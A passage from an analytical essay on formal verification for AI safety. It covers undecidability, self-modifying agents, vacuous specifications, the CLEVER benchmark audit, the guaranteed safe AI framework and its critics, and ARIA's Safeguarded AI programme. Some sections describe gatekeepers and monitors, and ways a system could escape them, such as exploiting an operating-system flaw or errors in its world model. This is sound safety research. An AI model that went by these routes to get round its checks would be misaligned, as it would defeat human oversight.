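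The guarantee does not hold if the system can loop indefinitely. A language model may never produce the token that ends its response, and an agent may keep calling the model. Melo and colleagues would therefore add a counter that forces the whole system into a final state after a fixed number of steps.

They acknowledge that guaranteeing a system halts makes its alignment decidable, but doesn't make the system aligned or ensure that checking it takes little computation. They suggest that designers aim for about 2⁸⁰ possibilities rather than 2^1,000,000. One computer checking a billion possibilities per second would still need 38 million years for 2⁸⁰. Halting also doesn't prevent harm, since an agent can delete the backups in its first step and then halt on schedule.

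The other proposal is more useful. The published version, *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (2025), argues that developers should start from a few components with proven properties and combine them only in ways that preserve those properties. Infinitely many systems can be built this way, and each comes with a proof that it has those properties.

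### Does undecidability make alignment unverifiable?

Several papers draw much stronger conclusions. Agarwal (2026), in *No Certificate for Alignment*, argues that no verifier can be sound, complete and fast over an unlimited range of inputs, though it can have any two of these properties. Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, concludes that no fully general system can be permanently certified as safe. *Neurodivergent influenceability in agentic AI as a contingent solution* (2026) uses theorems of Gödel and Turing to argue that any sufficiently expressive AI system will behave unpredictably.

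Rice's theorem only rules out a single procedure that gives the right answer about every program. It doesn't imply that any particular program's safety is unprovable. An agent whose entire code is "do nothing" is easy to prove safe, and the payment agent is only slightly harder. A company that wants to deploy an agent needs a proof about that agent alone, and it can choose a design that makes the proof easy.

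Großmann (2026), in *AI Alignment Is Neither Solvable nor Sufficient*, accepts that narrow objectives are achievable under restricted conditions and that worst-case results don't make every system hard to verify. But he argues that worst-case analysis is still appropriate for general guarantees, because these must hold in rare and difficult cases too. This is right about inputs, since a proof about an agent should cover the strangest message it might receive. But Rice's theorem concerns the worst case over all programs, including those designed to defeat the verifier, and a developer can decline to use those.

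A sound checker can also return "unknown". For example, a checker that accepts an agent only if its code tests for an approval immediately before every deletion would reject the agent built from P above without determining whether P halts. If P runs forever, the agent is harmless and the rejection is a mistake, but the agent had no practical use. Type checkers have worked this way for decades.

Agarwal shows the same behaviour on a small network with two inputs. Interval bounds proved a minimum output when the check covered up to 49% of the intended region, but returned "inconclusive" when it covered 64% or more. Splitting the region into smaller pieces, as verifiers normally do, might have proved more.

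#### Verifiers that read the code

Agarwal's second argument is that a fast verifier can try only finitely many inputs, so an unsafe system could behave well on all of them. His example is a family of functions that output 1 when the input x is greater than a parameter θ, and 0 otherwise. A function counts as aligned if θ is at most 0.05. An aligned function with θ = 0.04 and an unaligned one with θ = 0.06 agree on every input below 0.04 or above 0.06, so tests on those inputs can't distinguish them.

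But Agarwal's definition gives the verifier the system itself, including its parameters. A program that reads θ only has to compare it with 0.05. Even a single test at x = 0.05 would separate these two functions. The argument is sound for evaluations that only try prompts and look at the responses, which is how people test most language models today. It doesn't apply to proofs, which cover infinitely many inputs by reasoning about the code.

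Gumbau Mezquita makes a similar assumption when he says that any verifier that finishes can inspect only a limited part of a system's behaviour. He also argues against Melo and colleagues that an algorithm can in principle check one finite configuration, but no algorithm can decide which statements hold in all finite configurations. The second claim is Trakhtenbrot's theorem, from 1950, which, like Rice's theorem, excludes only a general procedure. Individual statements can still have short proofs. For example, a paragraph is enough to prove that "every sent payment was approved" holds for every finite number of payments.

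Agarwal also notes that the undecidability result doesn't cover deployed language models, because their context and precision are limited. Nobody has proved any broad safety property for today's large language models, because training produces billions of parameters with no structure designed to support a proof.

For harm and deception, choosing the causal model and the other inputs is a bigger difficulty than undecidability. People have to make these choices, and no theorem about computation helps them do it.

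### Systems that run without end or rewrite themselves

An inductive invariant like the payment agent's is enough for a system that never stops. If nobody finds one, people can still check a limited number of steps or rely on a monitor.

Self-modification is harder because the steps can change. Gumbau Mezquita represents it as a function Φ that turns one version's code into the next. He proves that if Φ makes at least one safe program unsafe, and meets some technical conditions, no algorithm can decide for every program whether its next version will have the same safety status. He infers that only a system that has stopped changing its behaviour can have a lasting certificate, and that no algorithm can tell whether the next version will be safe, even if the present one is known to be.

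His own example contradicts the last part. In it, "safe" means that a program gives an answer for every input, and Φ removes the answers for every input except 0. The next version is therefore always unsafe, so an algorithm that predicts "unsafe" every time is always right. The theorem holds in this example only because no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary present version is safe.

A proof can also remain valid while the system changes. Suppose the payment agent may rewrite the part that decides which bills to pay and when, but not the part that checks approvals and sends money. Its behaviour might change every day for years, but no version could send an unapproved payment. The proof holds for any output from the part that changes, as in the proofs about agent frameworks. Gumbau Mezquita concedes that his theorem need not apply if designers restrict the permitted changes, though the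 system would then lose some capacity for self-improvement.

If a system's whole program may change, the system can be required to prove each new version safe before switching to it. A small, fixed checker is enough to verify these proofs, because checking a proof is much easier than finding one. This also answers the argument that only another general AI could supervise a general AI, and that this supervisor would then need its own supervisor. The old version must stay in control until the check is finished, since otherwise the new one would act without a certificate. Some good improvements will be delayed because nobody can find a proof that they are safe.

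The checker is the hardest part to replace. By Gödel's second incompleteness theorem, a consistent formal system that includes basic arithmetic cannot prove its own consistency. A checker based on such a system therefore cannot prove the consistency of a successor that accepts everything it accepts and more. People can still trust a stronger checker, but only on other grounds. The simplest policy is to bar the system from rewriting its checker.

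Like the PocketFlow proof, all of these methods assume that the system can act only through the channels in the model. That assumption becomes less reliable with each version of a self-improving system. A later version of the payment agent might find a flaw in the operating system that the first one could not, and use it to send money through the bank's website.

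## What is a proof worth if the specification or the model of the world is wrong?

A correct proof can still fail to protect anyone, either because the specification doesn't express what people wanted or because the world doesn't behave like the model. Rechecking the proof won't reveal either problem.

### A rule that is true and empty

Suppose a company wants its agent to delete a file only after someone has approved the deletion, and to log every deletion. An engineer writes "every approved deletion is logged" as

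∀d : Deleted(d) and Approved(d) ⇒ Logged(d).

A rule might say that if a user approves a deletion, the agent logs it. But if nobody has connected the approval screen, nobody ever approves anything. In logic, an "if … then" statement is true whenever its "if" part is false, so a verifier will prove the rule even if the agent deletes files without asking and logs none of the deletions. Verification engineers call a property vacuous if it holds only because its condition never occurs.

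Connecting the screen would not repair the rule, which places no restriction on unapproved deletions. A better version is

∀d : Deleted(d) ⇒ Approved(d) and Logged(d).

The table compares the two rules on five programs.

| Program | First rule | Second rule |
|---|---|---|
| Deletes only approved files and logs each deletion | Holds | Holds |
| Deletes only approved files but logs nothing | Fails | Fails |
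| Deletes files without asking and logs nothing | Holds | Fails |
| Never deletes anything | Holds | Holds |
| Deletes only approved files and writes a blank log entry for each | Holds | Holds |

The program that never deletes anything is safe but useless, so the company also needs a liveness property. The program with blank log entries satisfies both rules but defeats the purpose of the log, which was to let someone find out later what the agent had deleted.

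### Wrong specifications in a benchmark

Specialists make such mistakes even in small problems. CLEVER is a set of 161 short programming tasks in Lean, each with an English description and a reference specification that a person wrote. An AI system has to write its own specification from the description and prove it equivalent to the reference. It then has to write a program and prove that it satisfies the reference.

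In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) ran three AI agents (Claude Opus 4.6, GPT-5.4 and Kimi K2.5) on all 161 CLEVER tasks and asked them to report any task that a mistake had made impossible. The audit found arguably wrong reference specifications in 80 of the tasks, and the CLEVER team reviewed and accepted every finding.

In 48 of the 80, the mistake was in how someone had expressed the idea in Lean. Twelve involved the order in which Lean applies operators, and 15 used "and" where the rule needed "if … then". For example, suppose a program should return the largest number in a list. A sensible rule is "If the list contains numbers, the result is the largest of them." No program can always satisfy "The list contains numbers and the result is the largest of them", because the list might be empty. The other mistakes concerned meaning, most often a misreading of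 the English description.

Impossible specifications also undermine CLEVER's test of equivalence, which is

∀f : (∀x : P(f, x)) ⇔ (∀x : Q(f, x)),

where f is any program, x is any input, and P and Q are the two specifications. If no program satisfies P and none satisfies Q, both sides are false for every f, so the equivalence holds. One could prove in this way that a faulty specification of "largest" is equivalent to a faulty specification of "smallest". Claude proved two such empty equivalences. Sosso and colleagues recommend comparing P and Q input by input, or requiring an example program that satisfies each.

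The three agents often proved programs correct against flawed reference specifications (34, 33 and 24 of them), and did so more often when the mistake made the specification too weak. Attempting a proof exposed only about half of the flawed references, whereas comparing each reference with an independently written specification exposed most of them.

The audit also shows that much of CLEVER's apparent difficulty came from defects in the benchmark. The best systems in the original evaluation completed 1 of the 161 tasks, and the new agents completed up to 59 under the same scoring. When Sosso and colleagues accepted any valid reading of each task's description and left out four tasks with other defects, Claude completed 151 of the remaining 157.

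Benchmarks get less scrutiny than flight software, so the audit doesn't suggest that half of all industrial specifications are wrong. But CLEVER's tasks are single short functions, and a specification for an AI agent would be much longer.

### Testing a specification

A vacuity check tests whether the rule ever applies. For the first deletion rule, an engineer would use a model checker to search for a run in which the agent deletes a file that someone has approved for deletion. If no such run exists, the rule is vacuous.

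One can also test a specification by breaking the program on purpose and checking whether the verifier rejects it, but the result depends on the fault chosen. If the engineer removes the line that writes the log, the program fails the first deletion rule, so the rule looks sound. Only removing the approval check shows that the rule is too weak, because the program still passes.

A further precaution is to write the specification without seeing the code, because someone who has read the code may just describe what it does. If the code deletes files without asking, they might write "the agent deletes the files it chooses", which is true but useless as a safety property. Moon and Varshney built this precaution into the pipeline that verified PocketFlow. The language model that writes the safety property is given the interface and a template of typical properties, but not the code, and the later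 step that has access to the code can't change the property.

Their pipeline applies its other tests to the proof instead of the program. In one, it reduces the helper invariant to almost nothing and empties the lemmas' proofs. In another, a language model inserts a plausible modelling error. Dafny has to reject both versions before the pipeline accepts the specification.

Moon and Varshney compared specifications written with and without access to the code for two example agents. For the agent that reads files, the difference was small, and neither specification merely restated the code. The comparison revealed more for the agent that looks up documents, because the template had no field for what that agent does. The model without access to the code used an existing field as a stand-in, which gave the property about that field some content. The model with access left the field empty because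 of the mismatch, so the property was vacuously true.

This empty property passed all the tests, which examined the invariants of the agent's main loop but not each part of the safety property. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that every field a property mentions can become non-empty in some run. Four runs on two agents are too few to show how much hiding the code helps, but they show that a specification can pass several sensible tests and still be empty.

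### From English to logic

Rules for agents usually start in English, and language models increasingly translate them into logic. *Safe Autoformalization* (2026) cites a 2023 system that was over 95% accurate at translating sentences into temporal logic, which can express "always" and "eventually". The same method now extends to security and access policies. But if errors are independent and each rule has a 95% chance of being translated correctly, a policy with 20 rules has only a 36% chance of being error-free.

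*Automatic Translation of Unstructured Requirements into Linear Temporal Logic* (2026) tested general-purpose language models on 15 loosely worded requirements. Eleven translations were perfect or nearly perfect. The models did badly on a requirement that depended on who was acting. The paper recommends that people check all formulas about roles, and complex ones with "if … then". Rules about permission tend to have both features, as in "if the account's owner approves, the agent may pay".

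Models also misuse the formal language, cover only the common cases, or forget part of a sentence, according to *Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026). Sometimes no translation is right because the English has no single meaning. *Bridging Natural Language and Formal Specification* (2025), which tested its method on aerospace requirements, gives the phrase "as soon as possible" as an example. Suppose an agent must stop as soon as possible after its user withdraws approval. Two possible translations are

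G (withdrawn → X stopped) and G (withdrawn → F stopped),

where G means "always", X means "at the next step" and F means "at some later point". The first may be impossible to satisfy if a payment is already under way, while the second allows the agent to carry on for a year. Someone has to choose a deadline. The aerospace system shows engineers an intermediate version of each requirement that they can correct.

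Translating a requirement into logic and back can catch some errors automatically. *Neurosymbolic Auditing of Natural-Language Software Requirements* (2026) describes VERIMED, a system that translates a medical-device requirement into logic, puts the formula back into English, and translates that English into logic again. A solver then checks whether the two formulas are equivalent. If they aren't, the meaning changed in translation. If they are, that is weaker evidence that the translation is right, because a model may consistently turn "as soon as possible" into "eventually", and then the formulas match even though both are wrong.

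### When AI writes the proofs

When a proof assistant checks a proof, people don't need to read the proof, but they still have to read the theorem. Mascherbauer and Aichernig (2026) make this point in *A Verified Implementation of the L\*-Algorithm in Lean*, about their verification of an algorithm by Dana Angluin. The algorithm learns which words belong to an unknown language by asking a teacher whether a particular word belongs, or whether a small machine it proposes recognises the language. The teacher accepts the machine or returns a word that the machine gets wrong.

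Mascherbauer and Aichernig's project has about 2,400 lines of Lean, roughly three quarters of them proofs. They wrote the core themselves. Claude Code, running Claude Opus 5.5, later added the final theorems, which state that the learned machine is correct, as small as possible and unique. Lean checked every proof. Mascherbauer and Aichernig write that the remaining task for a human reviewer is to check that the theorem statements express the intended properties.

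The correctness theorem assumes that the teacher accepts only correct machines. The teacher in the project's example tests 500 random words and accepts the machine if it finds no mistake, so the theorem doesn't apply to it. The uniqueness theorem does apply, but it concerns machines that recognise the language with no more states than the learned one. If the learner stops too early with a wrong machine, that machine has too few states, so no machine meets the condition and the theorem is vacuously true. Mascherbauer and Aichernig explain both points, but someone who read only the theorems' names could easily miss them.

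The statements are also easier to check because they use the standard definitions in Mathlib, Lean's main mathematical library. A reviewer can rely on definitions that many people have already examined instead of learning new ones.

AI can also help with the reading, as it did in the CLEVER audit. It could, for instance, find cases in which two candidate specifications disagree. A manager who can't read logic can still answer a question about such a case, such as "Should the agent be allowed to delete this file?" But a model reviewing a specification it wrote may repeat its original misreading.

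### The guaranteed safe AI framework

Even a specification that expresses exactly what people want reaches the world only through a model. The vancomycin proof was correct for a drug that patients swallow, but hospitals usually give this one through a vein. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, want the developers of powerful AI to make such models explicit. Their framework has three parts:

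- A world model describes mathematically how the AI system's outputs affect its environment.
- A safety specification states which effects are acceptable.
- A verifier produces a proof or a numerical bound showing that the system meets the specification in the world model.

Without a world model, a proof can cover only how a system's outputs depend on its inputs. Adding a world model lets the specification also cover outcomes, such as whether anyone gets hurt. The paper ranks approaches to each part by how much safety they would provide if they worked.

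| Part | Lowest level | Intermediate level | Highest level |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model | None, with assumptions hidden in the training data | Causal models that human experts have fully audited | None needed, because the specification holds in every possible world |
| Specification | None | Hand-written rules for limited properties | Everything people might want in every context |
| Verifier | No numerical guarantee | Automated search for inputs that cause failures | A sound bound on the probability of failure, with a proof short enough for people to read |

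The guarantee can take the model's errors into account. Suppose the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step. A system that provably meets the specification for n steps in the model then meets it in reality with probability at least

(1 − ε)ⁿ.

A car that makes ten decisions a second makes 36,000 in an hour. The bound for an hour is about 96.5% if ε is one in a million, but only 2.7% if ε is one in ten thousand. The true figure may be much higher, since most errors in a model don't cause accidents.

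But ε has to come from data or judgement, and it may change. An AI system that optimises hard against the model may find the situations where the model is wrong, and ordinary driving data would not reveal how often that happens. Dalrymple and colleagues raise a similar problem for specifications, where a simple stand-in for harm may work well until a capable system optimises against it.

People are the hardest part of the world to model. The paper suggests listing things a person might do and requiring the proof to cover all of them, without predicting which she will choose. As with proofs that assume a language model might output anything, this works only if the system can stay safe in every listed case. If a pedestrian may step in front of a car at any moment, no proof can rule out a collision unless the car always drives slowly enough to stop.

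### Dickson's objections

Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, argues that formal verification won't soon provide strong guarantees against the major AI threats. He uses the Perseverance rover's 2021 landing on Mars to show what verification normally covers. Engineers had verified that the lander's software wouldn't fail because of internal bugs, but they had no proof that the landing would succeed, or even that the computer's transistors would work. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and by one estimate perfect software would remove only a fifth of the risk.

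Dickson next objects that nobody has models of the things that matter most. One proposal was to require proof that a machine for making DNA can't produce anything harmful. He argues that predicting what a new virus would do to a person would require simulating a whole human body for years. In 2022, a leading simulation covered a single very simple cell for 20 minutes of simulated time. A human body has about 36 trillion cells, most of them far more complicated. A chatbot's effects are no easier to model, because its developers can't know who will repeat an answer or where, and a true statement can mislead people out of context.

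Even a perfect model would need data about the present state of the world. Google researchers who mapped a millionth of a human brain produced 1.4 petabytes of data, and at that rate a whole brain would take more than a million petabytes. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge in a footnote that perfect knowledge of physics would not reveal whether a molecule is toxic without facts about human cells.

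A proof about a physical device may not apply to the one a buyer receives, because the factory may have made a mistake or someone may have added a back door. Dickson thinks buyers would need continual physical inspections. Users of a chatbot on the internet are in a worse position, because they can't inspect the computer that runs it.

### Do the models have to be exact?

*In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* (Ammann, 2025) replies that a model can be accurate without being exact. A model that predicts only that a temperature will stay below 50 degrees is right if the temperature does so. Engineers call such a model a sound overapproximation, because it allows everything that can happen and perhaps more. It also needs less data about the starting state than an exact one. The interval bounds for neural networks work the same way.

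Her example for biology is a test of whether a virus can infect people. One would check every protein of the virus against every protein on the surface of human cells, instead of simulating a body. If no pair could let the virus into a cell, the virus would be safe. The test would wrongly reject some useful gene therapies, which also have to enter cells.

This problem is much smaller than Dickson's but still far from solved. Ammann concedes that nobody can yet carry out her full plan for protecting against dangerous DNA. It would require a sound way to predict how each pair of proteins interacts, and a method that was only usually right would not be enough. The test also covers only one route to harm, since DNA that encodes a toxin can be dangerous without being part of a virus.

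Some situations require only short-term predictions. In one design, a powerful controller runs a machine, with a simpler controller as backup. The verifier checks only that the backup could still bring the machine to safety after the next couple of steps. If the verifier can't confirm this, the backup takes over at once. A monitor also compares the world with the model's predictions and switches to the backup if they diverge. This design suits a power grid better than a conversation, where a harmful answer may be impossible to take back.

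Ammann proposes combining tamper-resistant hardware with cryptographic methods that tie a proof to a particular physical device. This addresses swapped or altered devices, but people then have to trust the hardware that does the checking.

Dalrymple and colleagues also defend world models in general. They argue that an AI system can carry out a complicated plan against humanity only if the world is predictable enough to plan in, in which case people should be able to build accurate models too. This argument seems hasty, because a verifier needs a model that covers every plan the system might try, while an attacker only needs to predict the results of one plan that works. Their stronger argument is that every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, and a formal model at least makes them explicit.

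### Designing systems that are easier to verify

Steve Omohundro, a co-author of the 2024 framework, commented under *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* that he agreed with most of its specific points but drew different conclusions. He later argued that engineers can design systems to make the proof manageable, instead of having to prove things about the world as they find it. Chip designers do this by following rules that keep circuits predictable.

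The DNA machine illustrates the difference. Omohundro says he and Max Tegmark never proposed that a computer should work out which sequences are safe. A biosafety board would draw up a list of permitted sequences, and a "gatekeeper" program would stop the machine from making anything else. The specification is then simply

∀s : Made(s) ⇒ s ∈ Permitted.

As with a payment agent, the machine can check this just by comparing a request with a list, without any proof about the human body. The engineers also need to show that nobody can bypass the gatekeeper, which requires a model of the device and of the attacks it must withstand.

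The reply is convincing for this narrower goal, but it relies on the board to judge which sequences are safe. The proof still holds if the board lists a dangerous sequence by mistake. A strict list would also block new sequences that researchers want to study, and someone might later join permitted fragments into something dangerous. The proof is possible because the design gives up some usefulness and the specification requires less than "this machine can do no harm".

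### Is formal verification overrated?

Zac Hatfield-Dodds maintains Hypothesis, a widely used tool that tests programs on automatically generated inputs. In his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* (Hatfield-Dodds, 2024), he says that he likes formal verification and wants it in a portfolio of safety methods, but objects to what people claim for it. He makes three main arguments.

He begins with neural networks. He thinks it is impossible to reason formally about their weights once there are billions of them, and that treating their rounded arithmetic as exact would make the conclusions irrelevant. Ammann largely agrees about the weights but replies that guaranteed safe AI checks what a system proposes to do, whatever network produced the proposal, and doesn't try to verify the weights themselves.

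Hatfield-Dodds's argument about world models is harder to answer. A developer who proves that a system is safe in a model still has to convince everyone that the model matches reality. He would rather she spent that time listing what could go wrong and explaining why it would or wouldn't happen. A formal model can help with this if it exposes a hidden assumption, but it adds much less if the disputed assumption is one of its inputs.

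He likes the idea of using AI to write verified software but doesn't think it can replace work on AI safety. Ordinary software can't match machine learning at the tasks machine learning does best, so people will still want machine learning systems even though they are less predictable. Building only AI tools that answer questions wouldn't help either. With a few lines of code, someone could turn such a tool into an agent by repeatedly asking it for the best next action and automatically carrying out the answer.

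In a comment under Ammann's reply, he added that advocates choose well-understood, closed domains and exclude natural language when they argue that the method is feasible, but point to the dangers of general AI when they argue that it matters. Ammann does restrict the method in this way, recommending it for power grids, supply chains and similar systems, and not for chatbots. She answers that many narrow applications could together make society much harder to attack. That is a good reason to fund the work, but it is a more modest claim than a guarantee about a general AI system.

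Hatfield-Dodds also called the agenda "vaporware" and asked for a demonstration. Another commenter thought this unfair less than a year after the framework appeared.

### ARIA's £59 million programme

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) has a £59 million programme called Safeguarded AI, which Dalrymple first directed. The original plan from 2024 was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work in safety-critical industries under mathematical guarantees. ARIA hoped this would build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind gatekeepers that check its actions.

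In November 2025, shortly before applications closed, the agency cancelled its plan to choose a team to develop specialised AI for the programme. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explains that general AI models had improved faster than he expected and would probably soon have the needed abilities anyway. The £18 million set aside for the specialised AI went to the programme's tools for writing models, specifications and proofs.

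ARIA then dropped its planned second call for projects on physical systems and turned to cybersecurity. According to the programme's page, *Safeguarded AI*, the physical projects were meant to demonstrate a safer way of offering AI than a general chat service, but rapid progress had disproved the hypothesis that dangerous AI systems might not become openly available. A gatekeeper can check only the systems that people run behind it, so a proof about one copy of a model doesn't protect against another copy that an attacker has downloaded.

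Nora Ammann, who wrote the reply to the critics, has since become the programme's director. In *Safeguarded AI*, the new thesis published in May, Ammann (2026) adds that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. The programme now aims to protect society by verifying security-critical software. A funding call that closed in July 2026 invited teams to build and verify components of such software, or to test them by attacking them.

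There is good evidence that software verification can work. In HACMS, an earlier American research programme, verified components withstood sustained attacks by security experts, even on a helicopter that carries people. The main obstacle was the human labour each proof took, and AI can now do much of it. The gap between model and world is also much smaller for software than for a human body, because software's designers know its code and can choose what it is allowed to do.

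ARIA said it changed course because of the speed of AI progress and the lack of political agreement. It has not reported that good world models are impossible, so the change doesn't show that the original method fails. Its existing projects on physical systems, including one that models pharmaceutical supply chains, will run to completion, and under the new thesis ARIA still hopes to reach energy, transport and medical devices later. But the programme has not shown that anyone can guarantee the safety of a powerful AI system acting freely in the world. It has moved its main effort to the area where Dickson and Hatfield-Dodds already expected formal verification to be useful.

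Commenters under Ammann's reply disagreed about whether securing software counts as AI safety. One thought it was valuable but separate. Another pointed out that AI companies can't yet protect their models from theft by a determined state, so any plan that relies on controlling a powerful model depends on better security.

Dalrymple's preferred first demonstration is a verified firewall for power grids, water systems and air traffic control, which increasingly send their data over the internet. Its proof could cover every message an attacker might send, however capable the attacker's AI, as long as the hardware behaves as modelled. People would still decide which messages to let through. If the rules let a grid operator shut down a power station remotely, a firewall that enforces them perfectly will also pass that command from someone who has stolen the operator's credentials. Ammann expects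 that, as AI produces more of the proofs, trust will increasingly depend on the specifications and assumptions, and part of the programme studies how to help people check them.
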